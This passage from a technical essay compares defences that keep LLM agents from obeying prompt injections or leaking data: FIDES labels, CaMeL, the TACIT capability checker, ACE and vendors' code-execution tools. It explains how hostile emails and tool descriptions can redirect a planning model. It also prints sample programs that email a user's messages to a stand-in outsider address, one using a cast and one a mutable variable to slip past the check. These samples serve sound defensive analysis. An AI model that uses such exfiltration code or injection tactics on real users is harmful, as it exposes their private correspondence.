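asks   = isolated_model("Does any of these ask for a meeting?", emails, answer=bool)
if asks:
    when = isolated_model("What date and time?", emails, answer=datetime)
    create_event(time=when)
```

The planning model writes both branches in advance, and the runtime follows the one that the answer selects. Some tasks that count as data dependent under the FIDES test therefore fit into a single program. A stranger's email still determines whether the last line runs, so the policy must allow or forbid that influence, as before.

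#### What the limit protects against

Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, use fixed forms for a different reason. They keep free text from the planning model but let through integers, decimal numbers, Booleans and choices from a vetted list, because none of these can express an instruction. In their shopping agent, the isolated model turns each customer review into two scores from 0 to 10, for how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is. The agent then uses the median of each score, which also limits the effect of a single dishonest review.

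This argument is sound for instructions, but it barely addresses secrets. An integer with no stated range can encode text of any length, so a reviewer concerned with confidentiality should ask for a range as well as a type. Jacob and colleagues do keep lists of values short so that an attacker can't spell out a message one number at a time.

Restricting answers to a fixed form also doesn't keep out false data. If a program asks which of three invoices is overdue, an attacker can write one that the model wrongly picks, and the answer is still valid. Jacob and colleagues excluded false data from their threat model and reported that no attacks succeeded. Zverev and colleagues included it when they tested UCM, an earlier defence that shows the planner fixed-form answers without tracking their influence on later calls. They let the attacker dictate every answer that the isolated model gave after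 reading hostile content. Between 4.6% and 6.8% of attacks succeeded, depending on the model.

Their own system makes no exception for small answers. If the planner looks at an untrusted Boolean, the whole context becomes untrusted, and the user has to approve any consequential action that follows. Costa and colleagues would let a policy accept the Boolean because they think a single bit is unlikely to convey a prompt injection. They left fixed-form answers out of their tests, so those tests don't show how well the exception works.

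Whether an untrusted answer may decide an action should depend more on the harm a wrong answer could do than on how many bits it contains. One untrusted bit can be allowed to decide whether to block out an hour in the user's calendar, because that is easy to undo. But one bit is also enough to trigger the payment of an invoice, which is not easy to undo. The types also don't track how many answers a program requests. Under the rules of a lattice, two Boolean answers joined together still have the type Boolean, even though together they can carry two bits.

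### When the planning model has to read the data

Fixed forms require someone to know the possible answers in advance. A program for the to-do list could sort each entry into "pay a known bill", "reply to an email" or "neither", with a branch for each category. But an entry such as "book the room Ana suggested, unless Ben has found something cheaper" would end up under "neither". The same problem arises when the data contains instructions the user wants the agent to follow, or when the next step depends on an explanation instead of a category.

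Designers can use fixed forms even for tasks that depend on free text, such as fixing a bug from a stranger's report. The coding agent needs some information about the bug, so Jacob and colleagues have the isolated model convert the report into a bug category, file numbers and line numbers. The planning model then works from a clean copy of the code, and it learns where to look but not what the person who reported the bug observed. *Twin Agent* (2026) objects more generally that the isolated model has to compress everything it has seen, although the planning model may need only a small part of it for the next decision.

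If no fixed form is sufficient, the planning model has to read the text itself. FIDES and SPIDES both have a tool that puts a hidden value into the context and joins its label to the context's label. For the to-do list, the effect on the context's label depends on who can write to the list. If only the user can, the context stays trusted and only its set of permitted readers shrinks. But in the example that opens Willison's 2023 post, a user asks an assistant to add the action items from Julia's latest email to a to-do list. The list then contains text that Julia influenced, so the app has to store her label with it. If the label is lost, the assistant will treat her words as the user's own when it is next asked to "carry out today's tasks".

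If the planning model reads untrusted entries, it loses the pattern's main protection and is as exposed as it is in the ordinary loop. The whole of any program it writes afterwards is untrusted, including recipients that seem to come from the user. If a provider runs the model, the provider also receives the text. The context's label never becomes less strict, so every later call in that context has the same problem.

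The trusted action policy still blocks a payment that the model chose after reading the entries, and the permitted flow policy still limits who can receive confidential data. If every consequential tool has a suitable policy, the agent is therefore no less secure, but it can do much less without asking the user. Without such policies, nothing prevents the agent from obeying the outsider.

Calls that the model chooses before it reads untrusted text are still trusted, so a planner should first complete the parts of a request that don't depend on that text. It should also avoid reading things it doesn't need. In one FIDES run, the user had already named the chat channel, but the model fetched the list of channels anyway, which made its context untrusted.

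An outsider may even be able to make the planner read the original data. Kolluri and colleagues let their isolated model reply with a fixed request for more information. They instruct the planner to supply more or, if it can't, to reconsider its plan and open the original data. A hostile email could make the isolated model give this reply every time. The labels would still prevent the planner from acting on what it read, but the user would have to approve steps that the agent could otherwise take alone.

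## Having the model write the program

For a task that doesn't depend on the data, the planning model needs the user's request, a description of each tool, and a statement of which programming language it may use. It should return only a program, or a statement that it can't write one. The designer chooses how to describe the tools and which language to permit, and both choices affect how well the model writes the program and how much a checker can establish about it.

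### Describing a tool as a typed function

Most developers describe a tool to a model with a JSON schema, a piece of structured text that lists the tool's inputs and the type of each. For the first tool in the Project X program, it could look like this:

```
{
  "name": "read_emails",
  "description": "Find emails in the user's mailbox.",
  "input_schema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
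      "topic":  {"type": "string",  "default": ""},
      "number": {"type": "integer", "default": 20}
    }
  }
}
```

The designer can also present the tool as a typed function, as a software library would:

```
class Email:
    sender:  Address
    sent:    datetime
    subject: str
    body:    str

def read_emails(topic: str = "", number: int = 20) -> list[Email]:
    """Find emails in the user's mailbox."""
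```

The most useful addition is the result type after the arrow. It lets the planning model write `email.sender` without having seen an email. Otherwise the model may have to call the tool once and read the result, which puts the emails into its context. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling*, the documentation for a product that runs generated code, advises developers who don't know the shape of a tool's results to keep that tool out of programs, so that the model can inspect the results. With protected data, this would expose the data to the model, so the developer should describe the results instead.

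A JSON schema can describe a tool's results as well as its inputs, and OpenAI's product has a separate field for describing results. But converting a schema into a function can't add information that the schema lacks. In *Code Mode*, a post on Cloudflare's blog, Varda and Pai convert a documentation server's tools into functions in TypeScript, a typed version of JavaScript. Every field of every result in their example has the type `any`, presumably because the server described only its inputs. The model then has to guess the field names, and a type checker can't check those guesses.

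Varda and Pai found that agents could handle more tools, and more complicated ones, when the tools were presented as functions. They attribute this to the training data, which includes real code from millions of open-source projects but only a small, artificial set of tool calls. The explanation is plausible, though their post contains no test scores. Anthropic points out that a schema defines which calls are structurally valid but can't express which optional inputs belong together. Most typed function signatures can't express this either, so a comment or a worked example has to explain it.

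The benefit is larger for a checker. A schema lets software validate one call at a time, once the values exist, whereas typed functions let a type checker examine the whole program before any tool has run. The type checker can reject `send_email(to=emails, body=summary)` because a list of emails is not an address. The program's text also shows which expression goes into `to` and which into `body`, so the checker can apply a separate limit to each. Types don't replace labels, however, because an address that an outsider planted in an email also has the type `Address`.

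The planning model's context includes the tool descriptions. In Varda and Pai's example, one description includes an instruction to call that tool first whenever the user asks about a certain product. This instruction is harmless, but a hostile supplier could put a prompt injection in the same place, and the planning model would read it before writing any code. The deployer should therefore review every description or write it from scratch. Microsoft's *agent-framework-hyperlight* (2026), the documentation of a package that runs generated code, also warns developers not to put credentials or customer identifiers into descriptions or default values, because the model can see them.

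### A list of calls, a small language or a general one

Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, the documentation of a similar product, gives the example of checking the spending of 20 employees against their budgets. In Python, a general-purpose language, the program could look like this:

```
over = []
for person in list_employees(team="Sales"):
    spent = sum(item.amount for item in read_expenses(person))
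    if spent > read_budget(person):
        over.append(person)
show_user(over)
```

The last line displays the names to the user without returning them to the model.

A fixed list of calls can do only part of this. If the user names the 20 employees, the list can contain 40 calls that fetch their expenses and budgets. It can't add up the amounts or leave out the people who stayed within their limits, unless a tool does that. It also can't cover a team whose size nobody knows in advance. But a fixed list is easy to analyse. It has only one path, so the checker works out one label per result and compares each argument once.

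The list should also refer to data by name. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues leave the message to the boss blank in their plan for the calendar task. If the planning model fills it in after reading the calendar, the calendar data still passes through the model's context.

A small purpose-built language has only the features its designer chooses to include. The budget program needs named results, a loop over a list, an `if`, addition and comparison. The language can leave out everything else, so its programs can open files or contact websites only through a tool. The checker needs one rule for each construct. For an `if`, it has to consider both branches, because which one runs depends on the data. If loops can only run over finite lists, every program ends, provided that the tools do.

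This makes more work for the designer, who has to write an interpreter for the language and guess which operations users will need. The model has also never seen the language in training, so Varda and Pai's complaint about artificial tool calls applies here too. Borrowing Python's syntax probably reduces this problem, but the model will then sometimes use a Python feature that the small language doesn't have.

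A restricted general language is a language such as Python or TypeScript with its dangerous features forbidden. The model can then parse dates, group records and define its own functions in a language it knows well. Its programs are much harder to analyze because they can change variables repeatedly, pass functions to other functions, and build text that they then run as code. Rice's theorem implies that no checker can correctly decide, for every program in an unrestricted general language, whether the program will ever do something like send a salary to an outsider. A checker that never accepts an unsafe program must therefore reject some safe ones.

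The restrictions must at least ban constructs that hide which tool a line calls, such as running text as code or looking up a function by a computed name. This is hard to do completely in Python, because a program can reach unexpected functions through an object's ordinary attributes. A language with a stricter compiler can enforce some of these restrictions itself, as Scala does in the system TACIT.

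A few constructs in Python syntax are probably the best starting point for an office assistant, with any complicated processing moved into tools that the developer has written and tested. Most email and calendar tasks need little more than a loop and a condition. A team that expects users to ask for free-form data analysis will need more of the language and a checker that can handle the additional constructs.

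CaMeL is the best-known research system of this kind. SC Media, a security trade publication, describes CaMeL's defence as a deterministic policy engine, outside the model, that decides whether to execute the actions the model proposes. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues write that extracting the control flow and data flow explicitly, as CaMeL does, may also help people who must approve an agent's actions.

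### Generated code as a product

Companies adopted generated code mainly to save tokens and time. In November 2024 Anthropic launched the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting agents to tools, and developers were soon connecting agents to hundreds or thousands of tools. The tools' descriptions alone could fill much of the model's context. Cloudflare's Code Mode gives the model a single tool that runs TypeScript, and that code can call all the other tools as functions. Anthropic recommended the same approach in a November 2025 post. In its version, each tool is a code file in a folder, and the model opens only the files it needs.

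The post reports that this last step cuts token use from 150,000 to 2,000. All of that saving comes from tool descriptions that the model no longer reads in advance, not from keeping data out of the context. Anthropic gives a separate example for data, in which the transcript of a two-hour sales meeting has to go from Google Drive into a customer record. In the ordinary loop, the transcript passes through the model twice, which could add 50,000 tokens.

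Anthropic's later measurements are more modest. On a benchmark with 75 project-management tools, generated code reduced billed input tokens by about 38% without changing accuracy. On τ²-bench, a benchmark of airline, retail and telecom tasks where each turn needs only one or two calls, it left the scores unchanged and cost about 8% more. Microsoft claims that in typical workloads with many tool calls, its version can roughly halve the delay and cut token use by more than 60%. These vendors' figures for their own products suggest that generated code saves most when a program makes many calls or handles large results, and that it may save little on a short task like the Project X summary.

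Microsoft calls its version CodeAct. Microsoft (2026) introduced it in April, and the model reaches tools from inside a Python program through a function named `call_tool(...)`. The products differ in language and in what a developer can restrict:

| Product | Language | How output gets back to the model | What the developer can restrict |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, programmatic tool calling | Python | Printed text and error messages | Which tools code should call, although the setting only guides the model |
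| OpenAI, Programmatic Tool Calling | JavaScript | `text(...)` and `image(...)` | Which tools code can call, with approval for some of them |
| Varda and Pai, Code Mode | TypeScript | `console.log()` | Which tools code can reach, with no other internet access |
| Microsoft, CodeAct | Python | One combined result, plus files from an output folder | Which tools, folders and web domains code can reach |

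Anthropic's managed product does not let code call tools that come through its MCP connector, although the 2025 post was about MCP. A developer can still define the same tool separately and have the application call the MCP server.

Cloudflare has since reduced tool descriptions further. *Code Mode*, a later post with the same main title, describes giving the model just two tools for an entire large service, one to search its documentation and one to execute code. According to Cloudflare's documentation, the executed code gets a general function for making authenticated requests, which makes checking harder. A policy for `send_email` applies to any call with that name, but a checker that finds a general web request has to determine what it will do from its address and contents.

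Google's offering is harder to compare because it is unclear whether a program written by Gemini can itself call a developer's functions. Google's *Code execution* describes a tool in the Gemini API that runs code the model has written, for work such as solving equations or processing text. Google's *Gemini API Code Execution tool for ADK* warns that an agent with this tool can't have any others in Google's Agent Development Kit. Schmid (2026), in *Combine Built-in Tools and Function Calling in the Gemini Interactions API*, reports that developers can now combine Google's built-in tools with their own functions in one request. But there the model chooses each call and the API passes context between the tools, as in an ordinary loop.

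### Whether the data really stays out of the context

Anthropic's 2025 post presents privacy as a further benefit. Intermediate results stay in the execution environment by default, and the agent sees only "what you explicitly log or return". In practice the model writes the program, so the model decides what to log. Each of the four products in the table accepts some version of this:

```
emails = read_emails(topic="Project X")
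print(emails)
```

These two lines put every email into the context. A model may write them for ordinary reasons, such as checking the format of the result or reading the emails to write a summary the user asked for. Anthropic's example of a finished run prints the five largest customers and their revenue because the model needs them to answer the user. The default therefore reduces how much data reaches the model, but a developer can't tell a client that no data will reach it.

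The printed text also makes prompt injection possible again, because in all four products the model reads the output and can then write another program. If the output contains an email from a stranger, the model is as exposed to injection as it is in the ordinary loop.

Error messages can also carry data back to the model. Anthropic's product returns error output to the model, which helps it repair its code, but an error about an unreadable date may quote the email that contained it. Microsoft replaces tool errors with a generic message by default. Developers can turn the details back on, but Microsoft warns that they may contain sensitive data.

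A builder who needs a guarantee can leave the output function out of the permitted language, so that only the runtime can display results, and only to the user. Alternatively, the builder can treat printing as a tool call with a policy of its own:

```
print(text)
    the call   integrity T
    text       integrity T; readers must include the model's provider
```

This policy lets the program return today's date but not the emails or anything computed from them. The policy must also apply to errors and any files the program returns.

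Data can also reach the provider without reaching the model. In Anthropic's managed product, the developer's application sends each tool result to a container on Anthropic's side, where the program uses it and continues running. Anthropic keeps container data for up to 30 days and excludes the feature from its zero-retention arrangement. OpenAI also runs the programs itself but supports zero retention for customers who have it enabled, depending on the tools they use. An office that is not allowed to send its clients' correspondence to a provider has to run the programs on its own machines. Anthropic says this is safe if the code runs in a sandbox (an environment cut off from the rest of the system), but complex to build and maintain.

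#### Placeholders for personal data

For more sensitive work, Anthropic's 2025 post proposes replacing personal data with placeholders. Suppose a user wants to copy customers' contact details from a spreadsheet into Salesforce. The procedure has four steps:

1. The program asks for the rows of the spreadsheet.
2. The software that connects the agent to its tools finds the names, email addresses and phone numbers in the result, stores them in a table, and puts a placeholder in the position of each.
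3. The program passes the rows on to the Salesforce tool. If the program prints a row, the model sees placeholders.
4. The connecting software looks up each placeholder and sends the real value to Salesforce.

This protects the contact details even from a careless `print`, which the default does not. It works well for data with a recognisable form, such as phone numbers, but much less well for free text, where a sentence about a colleague's operation may contain no name or number that the software can find. If the program printed a spreadsheet cell that also contained a prompt injection, the injection would reach the model unchanged. The program also has to work without the real values, so it couldn't, for example, sort customers by the company in their email address.

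The lookup in step 4 also needs a policy. If it works for every tool, a manipulated model can put a placeholder into a message to an outsider, and the software will fill in the real address. Anthropic mentions that developers can use the mechanism to define rules on where data may flow, but leaves developers to write them.

### How far products enforce data-flow rules

SC Media's August 2026 article, published in a sponsored section, states that no mainstream agent product had adopted CaMeL or the dual LLM pattern, and names Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI. First-hand evidence from Microsoft qualifies this claim.

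Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced in May that FIDES was available as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, the company's library for building agents. Developers could therefore use FIDES's labels and policies, along with the dual LLM pattern, in agents they built themselves.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a second experiment, in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. Users have to turn the experimental feature on with a flag. It keeps one label for the whole context and has policies for only some of the tools on GitHub's MCP server. The trade article is right that these patterns had not become standard in finished products, but readers could take its wording to mean that nobody had started building data-flow rules into one.

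The May announcement says that FIDES treats a tool without a label as trusted and public, but Microsoft's documentation says the tool's results are untrusted and public by default. Either way, if a developer forgets to label a client database, the system treats its records as fit for anyone to read.

All of this applies to ordinary tool calls. For generated programs, the clearest evidence is a warning in the version of Microsoft's package released on 12 November 2026. FIDES, which checks labels, does not work with CodeAct, which runs generated programs. FIDES normally checks a call as it passes through the agent's own software, but calls from inside a generated program take a different route and avoid the check. FIDES can check the outer request to run the program, but this does not enforce the policies of the tools that the program calls. If a developer registers a tool with a FIDES policy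 anyway, the package logs a warning and runs the code. Microsoft adds that the absence of a warning doesn't show that a setup is safe.

Microsoft advises developers to keep any tool that needs FIDES out of generated programs and have the model call it directly. OpenAI gives similar advice for actions that change something or need approval, because a direct call preserves a clear point of authorisation. Under this advice, the program for the Project X task would fetch and summarise the emails, and the model would request `send_email` itself. Unless the system also passes the summary by name, the model has to read it and write it out again, which the program was largely meant to avoid.

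Anthropic and OpenAI also tell developers to check permissions inside the application. This catches a message to an address outside a fixed list, but it can't determine whether an address came from the user's settings or was planted by a stranger. The runtime's request contains the argument values and an identifier for the program, but doesn't show where each value came from. Both products send the application the program's code along with its first request for one of the developer's own functions. A team can have a checker examine the code before the application carries out that request, although the program may already have used tools that the provider hosts. To check every call against labels, the team has to run the program in its own runtime.

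## Checking the program before it runs

Operating systems had to accept code from untrusted authors long before language models wrote any. An application may run its own code inside the kernel, the core of the system, where a faulty or hostile program can damage everything else. In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) proposed that the kernel publish a safety policy. The application then submits its machine code with a formal proof that the code obeys the policy, and the kernel checks the proof before it runs the code.

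*Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) is the classic version of this idea. A host can accept a program from any source if the program comes with a proof that it follows the host's policy. The program's author has to find the proof, which is the hard part. Checking it is quick and needs neither cryptography nor an outside authority. The host doesn't need to know or trust the author, because a false proof fails the check.

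The planning model is the untrusted author of a generated program, and the office is the host that runs it. In principle, the model could attach a proof that each program follows the policy, but someone would first have to state the policy in formal logic, and the model would have to be good at writing proofs.

A type checker requires less work from the program's author than a proof does. It applies one fixed set of rules to every program and works out most of the types itself, so the author adds only a few annotations. But it can establish only the properties that the type system was designed for. A proof can use any fact about a particular program, for example that a loop sends at most three messages because an earlier line shortened the list to three. An ordinary type checker can't verify that reasoning, and a type system that limited the number of messages would probably reject the program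 even though it is safe. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) choose types because precise specifications of what an agent should do are often unavailable or impractical.

### Capabilities as values

TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) is an MCP server from EPFL, a technical university in Lausanne. It accepts code written in Scala 3, a general-purpose language, and runs it only if it passes the Scala compiler's checks. Any agent that can use MCP tools can connect to TACIT, and the agent itself doesn't have to be written in Scala.

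A capability is an unforgeable value in a program that gives code that holds it permission to perform an action. In TACIT, a program that needs files from one folder calls `requestFileSystem` with the folder's name and a block of code. The library passes the block a capability for that folder, and the block can open files only through that capability.

Capabilities date from the 1960s, but earlier capability languages enforced them only while a program ran. Scala's compiler also records in a function's type which capabilities the function can use:

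```
String -> Int          can use no capability
String ->{mail} Int    can use the capability "mail"
String => Int          can use any capability
```

The compiler works out the set in braces from the function's body. It adds `mail` to the set if the body uses `mail` or calls another function whose set includes `mail`. A function with a smaller set can be used wherever one with a larger set is allowed, but not the other way round. A function with an empty set is called pure. It can calculate a result from its input, but it can't send, store or print anything.

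The same record stops a capability from leaving the block it was meant for. In one published example, an agent tried to return a list of file handles from a `requestFileSystem` block, which would have let later code use them. The type of each handle included the folder's capability, so the compiler rejected the program.

TACIT protects data with a wrapper called `Classified`. In simplified form:

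```
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
  def reveal(using CanAccess[T]): T
```

A program that holds a wrapped value can process the contents only by passing a function to `map`. The arrow in `T -> U` means this function must be pure, and `map` wraps the result again. The other method, `reveal`, returns the bare contents, but it requires a `CanAccess` capability that the agent never receives. Converting a wrapped value to text produces only `Classified(****)`.

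Passing results by name lets the planning model move data without reading it. With `map`, the model's program can also sort, count or shorten that data, still without the model seeing it.

### Two versions of the Project X program

To run the Project X task this way, a developer first has to supply typed tools. The following sketch is based on the email functions that Odersky and colleagues publish, with two changes. Sending mail requires a capability, and there is an extra function for sending protected text to the manager:

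```
def searchEmails(query: String): Classified[List[Email]]
def chat(prompt: String, message: Classified[String]): Classified[String]

class Mailer extends SharedCapability:
  def send(to: String, body: String): Unit
  def sendToManager(body: Classified[String]): Unit
```

`chat` calls the isolated model. It accepts wrapped text and returns a wrapped answer. If the runtime provides a `Mailer` named `mail`, the compiler accepts this program:

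```
val emails  = searchEmails("Project X")
val text    = emails.map { es => es.map(_.body).mkString("\n\n") }
val summary = chat("Summarise the progress reported here", text)
mail.sendToManager(summary)
```

The function on the second line only joins the emails into one text. It uses no capability, so `map` accepts it. The third line produces a `Classified[String]`, which is the type that `sendToManager` expects. The compiler can check all this before the program fetches any emails.

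Now suppose the user pasted a paragraph with an injection into the request, and the planning model wrote the attacker's program instead:

```
val emails = searchEmails("Project X")
emails.map { es => mail.send("outsider@example.com", es.head.body) }
```

The compiler rejects the second line with an error of this form:

```
Found:    (es: List[Email]) ->{mail} Unit
Required: List[Email] -> Unit
Note that capability `mail` cannot flow into capture set {}.
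```

The function's body uses `mail`, so the compiler adds `mail` to the function's set. `map` accepts only functions whose set is empty, so the compiler rejects the program before it runs. No email leaves the mailbox, whether the model was manipulated or made an honest mistake.

The attacker could try to send the summary directly with `mail.send("outsider@example.com", summary)`. This also fails to compile, because `send` expects plain text and `summary` is wrapped. Converting the summary to text first would compile, but the outsider would receive only the word "Classified" and four asterisks.

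The compiler would reject the same line even if the address were the manager's, because it checks whether the function can send anything, not who would receive it. The accepted program therefore needs `sendToManager`. The developer who writes this function decides that the manager may receive protected mail, and the function unwraps the text inside trusted code. The function should also apply the permitted flow policy while the program runs, because the type `Classified[String]` doesn't record that only the user and the manager may read Ben's email.

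The check also stops harmless code. In one published example, a program used an ordinary `write` inside `map` to save classified recommendations to a file in the folder of secrets. The write may have been harmless, but the compiler rejected it because the function passed to `map` held a file capability. The model has to use a separate function, `writeClassified`. Unlike an error from a running program, a compiler error can safely go back to the model because it contains only the program's code and types.

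### What the language has to rule out

Odersky and colleagues name three properties that the language needs for these guarantees to hold.

The first is capability safety, which means that a program can't forge a capability and the compiler can't lose track of one. Full Scala doesn't have this property because it allows casts. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type, without checking:

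```
val leak = (es: List[Email]) => mail.send("outsider@example.com", es.head.body)
emails.map(leak.asInstanceOf[List[Email] -> Unit])
```

The function still uses `mail`, but the cast gives the function a type with an empty set, so `map` would accept it. Reflection lets a running program look up methods and hidden fields by name, so code could also use it to reach inside the wrapper in a way the compiler can't detect in advance. TACIT therefore compiles the agent's code in a "safe mode" that forbids casts, reflection, and annotations that switch off individual checks.

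The second property, capability completeness, means that every action that matters for safety must require a capability unless the runtime can contain it. Scala programs can normally call Java's standard library, which can open a network connection without any capability, so a function that did this would look pure. Safe mode therefore lets agent code call a global function only if it was written under the same restrictions or marked as safe by the compiler or a library author. Agent code cannot call the ordinary global print functions.

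Changing a variable also counts as an action. Otherwise a program could carry a secret out of `map` without calling any tool:

```
var copy = ""
emails.map { es => copy = es.head.body }
mail.send("outsider@example.com", copy)
```

Safe mode tracks such changes, so the function on the second line isn't pure and the program fails.

Exceptions, the errors that interrupt a running program, are the main case left to the runtime. They can leak information, since a program could fail only when a secret has a certain value. But almost any line can fail, for instance by dividing by zero or running out of memory, so banning exceptions would be impractical. TACIT catches an exception and turns it into an ordinary value, which it can wrap like any other. This makes faults harder to find, because the runtime hides the error message when code inside `map` fails, and the user may see an empty result with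 no explanation.

Local purity, the third property, means that types can specify which capabilities, if any, one part of a program uses. The rest of the program can still send emails and write files.

Completeness depends on how developers write the tools, and the interfaces used in TACIT's own tests on AgentDojo probably don't achieve it. In the published version, `sendEmail` has no capability in its signature. The instructions to the model say that side effects inside `map` run immediately and that it should put "commits" where they should happen. This advice would make little sense if the compiler rejected every function with a side effect. In those tests, the wrapper seems to have kept strangers' text away from the agent without preventing a program from emailing that text to someone. A builder who wants the protection shown in the Project X example has to make every tool with side effects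 require a capability.

### Why Python is harder to check

Most developers would rather have the model write Python, which it knows better than Scala. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) argues that using Python makes strong guarantees difficult. It reports that CaMeL expresses its plans in a restricted subset of Python, and says that dynamic typing, control flow that depends on exceptions, and reflection make programs in the language harder to check before they run.

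Dynamic typing means that a name can refer to any kind of value, as in this function:

```
def deliver(channel, text):
    channel.send(text)
```

The call to `send` could email a client, write to a log or add a line to a list in memory, depending on what the caller passes as `channel`, and the function's text doesn't show which. Python doesn't enforce type annotations when the program runs, and they have no standard way to list capabilities. Almost any line can raise an exception and jump elsewhere, and a secret may determine whether that happens. With reflection, a program can call `getattr(tools, name)(text)`, where `name` is a string it built from other data.

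Tallam and Miller propose, but did not build, a purpose-built language with bounded loops, simple conditions, no reflection, and capability labels in its types. Their paper cites a different work as its reference for CaMeL, so it is a better guide to the general difficulty than to CaMeL itself.

Odersky and colleagues say that CaMeL's subset has no user-defined or recursive functions, and that a custom interpreter tracks the data while the program runs. They argue that if programs could define functions and pass them around, a checker that ran before the program would have to work out which functions might arrive at each call, and that doing this precisely takes exponential time in the worst case. In Scala, each function's type already includes the capabilities it holds, so the compiler can check functions one at a time.

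That argument comes from the designers of a competing system, but the result on computing time is older and independent of TACIT. That result matters only if programs need to define and pass functions, which the Project X program doesn't need to do. A sufficiently small subset of Python can therefore be checked in advance.

### Checking a plan against labels

*ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2025) uses a restricted language with Python's syntax so that programs can be checked before they run. Every program has a single `main()` function, and every variable has a declared type. Programs can't change a value in place, `for` loops can run only over a range of whole numbers, and there is no `break`. Each function call must be on its own line.

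ACE stands for Abstract-Concrete-Execute, after the three phases of the system:

1. A planning model reads the user's request and nothing else, not even the descriptions of the installed tools. It invents the tools it would like to have and writes a plan that uses them. For Project X, these might be `EmailFinder`, `TextSummarizer` and `EmailSender`.
2. A second model compares each invented tool with the installed ones, one pair at a time, and decides whether they match. It also writes a short adapter where the arguments differ. The checker then looks for a set of matches that satisfies the label rules, and stops if there is none.
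3. The runtime executes the plan, with each tool in its own container.

Keeping tool descriptions from the planning model addresses a threat that TACIT leaves to the developer. In a demonstration against an earlier system, IsolateGPT, Li and colleagues gave one ride-hailing app a description with an instruction to leave out a rival app. The planner left it out, and the user saw only one fare. In ACE, a description can affect only the match for its own tool. However, the matching model still reads hostile descriptions while it writes adapter code, and the label check covers the plan and the tools' clearances but not that code.

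Planning without seeing the tools can make tasks fail. When a user asked "Find my future flight", the planning model generated a hypothetical tool for finding future flights. The installed tool searched existing reservations, which was what the user needed, but the second model found no match between the descriptions, and the task failed. On InjecAgent, a benchmark of attacks hidden in tool results, the best pairing of models found the right tool in 82.1% of cases and completed 75.2%. No attack made the system call an attacker's tool because, by design, tool results never reach the planning models. The benchmark did not test the label check, which Li and colleagues show only on small examples.

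The label check uses the kind of lattice described earlier. A label here is a set of categories, such as "financial" or "medical", and each installed tool has a label as its clearance. The checker goes through the plan with two rules:

```
y = built-in operation on x1 ... xn
    label(y) becomes label(y) ⊔ label(x1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(xn)

y = call to tool f with x1 ... xn
    reject unless label(x1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(xn) ⊑ clearance(f)
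    label(y) becomes clearance(f)
```

In the published example, a plan loads the user's bank details and emails them. The data is labelled {financial}, but the email tool's clearance is {personal}, so the checker rejects the plan. The Project X plan passes if all three tools are cleared for project mail. If an outside provider runs the summariser and the deployer hasn't cleared it for that mail, the checker rejects the plan at the call to the summariser.

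The checker labels a tool's result with the tool's full clearance because the tool may have added data of its own. This can make labels stricter than necessary. Suppose the summariser has clearance for both project and financial data. The checker then treats every summary as containing financial data, and an email tool with clearance for project data alone can't send it, even if none of the summarised emails mentions money. Deployers should give each tool the lowest clearance it needs to do its work.

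Loops need extra care:

```
note = ""
for i in range(4):
    network_send(note)
    note = load_bank_details()
```

The loop's first pass sends an empty text and the second sends the bank details. A checker that read the lines once from top to bottom would miss this. ACE's checker repeats its analysis of the loop until the labels stop changing, so it finds that `network_send` receives financial data.

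A branch can reveal data without copying it. If a program sets `b` to 1 when a secret begins with a zero and to 2 otherwise, anyone who sees `b` learns whether the secret begins with a zero. This is called an implicit flow, while copying the data is an explicit flow. ACE's checker handles implicit flows by adding the condition's label to everything that happens inside the branch.

TACIT instead uses types to prevent such flows. The yes-or-no answer in the earlier calendar program would have the type `Classified[Boolean]`. An `if` needs a plain Boolean, so the program wouldn't compile, and a developer would have to supply a calendar tool that accepts `Classified` values. In ACE, the same program passes if the calendar tool has clearance for the emails' label.

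The two checks therefore prove different things about a program that passes:

| | TACIT | ACE |
|---|---|---|
| Main guarantee | Code that handles the contents of a wrapped value can't use a capability | No tool receives data above its clearance, even through loops and branches |
| Levels of secrecy | Wrapped or not wrapped | Any categories that the deployer defines |
| Sending protected text to the manager but not to an outsider | Possible with a special tool such as `sendToManager` | Not possible with one email tool, which has a single clearance for all addresses |
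| Sending a report to an address that the isolated model found in a stranger's email | Rejected if the tool expects a plain address | Accepted if the email tool has clearance for the data |
| Strangers' text in the planning model's context | Possible if nobody has wrapped the text | Excluded |

TACIT's guarantee holds whatever the emails contain, and so does ACE's if the labels are right. But neither check shows that the program does what the user asked, and neither covers timing or similar side channels.

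The best choice for an office assistant is probably a combination of ACE and TACIT. ACE's small language and category labels suit routine plans, and a deployer could add separate limits for each argument so that the checker can distinguish a message's recipient from its body. TACIT suits tasks that require substantial processing of protected data, such as comparing two versions of a contract, because its pure functions can use nearly all of Scala.

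### What still has to be trusted

Odersky and colleagues treat the hosted planning model, all the code it submits, and everything it reads, including the user's request, as potentially hostile. Their threat model therefore covers an injection pasted into the request. ACE, by contrast, treats the request as trusted, so a pasted injection can determine the whole plan, and only the label check then limits where data goes.

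TACIT's claim still depends on five kinds of component working correctly:

- The compiler has to apply its rules without error. Capture checking, the part that tracks capabilities, is still an experimental feature of Scala. Researchers have machine-checked proofs that the underlying type system is sound, but no corresponding proof yet that safe mode delivers the promised properties.
- The library has to guard every action it offers. The reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala, which a reviewer can read in full. Some library modules may bypass safe mode under the annotation `@assumeSafe`. An example is a cache that remembers earlier results in an untracked variable, where the programmer has to verify that the variable holds nothing else.
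- The runtime has to keep paths inside the permitted folder, hide wrapped values when it prints them and contain exceptions. It can't control what an external command does once a program has started it.
- The tool wrappers have to give each result the right type. If `searchEmails` returned a plain list of emails, the compiler would accept a program that sent them to anyone.
- Any model that reads protected data has to keep it to itself. The compiler can confirm that `chat` receives no capabilities, but not that the service behind it forgets each input afterwards. For this role, TACIT assumes a trusted local model.

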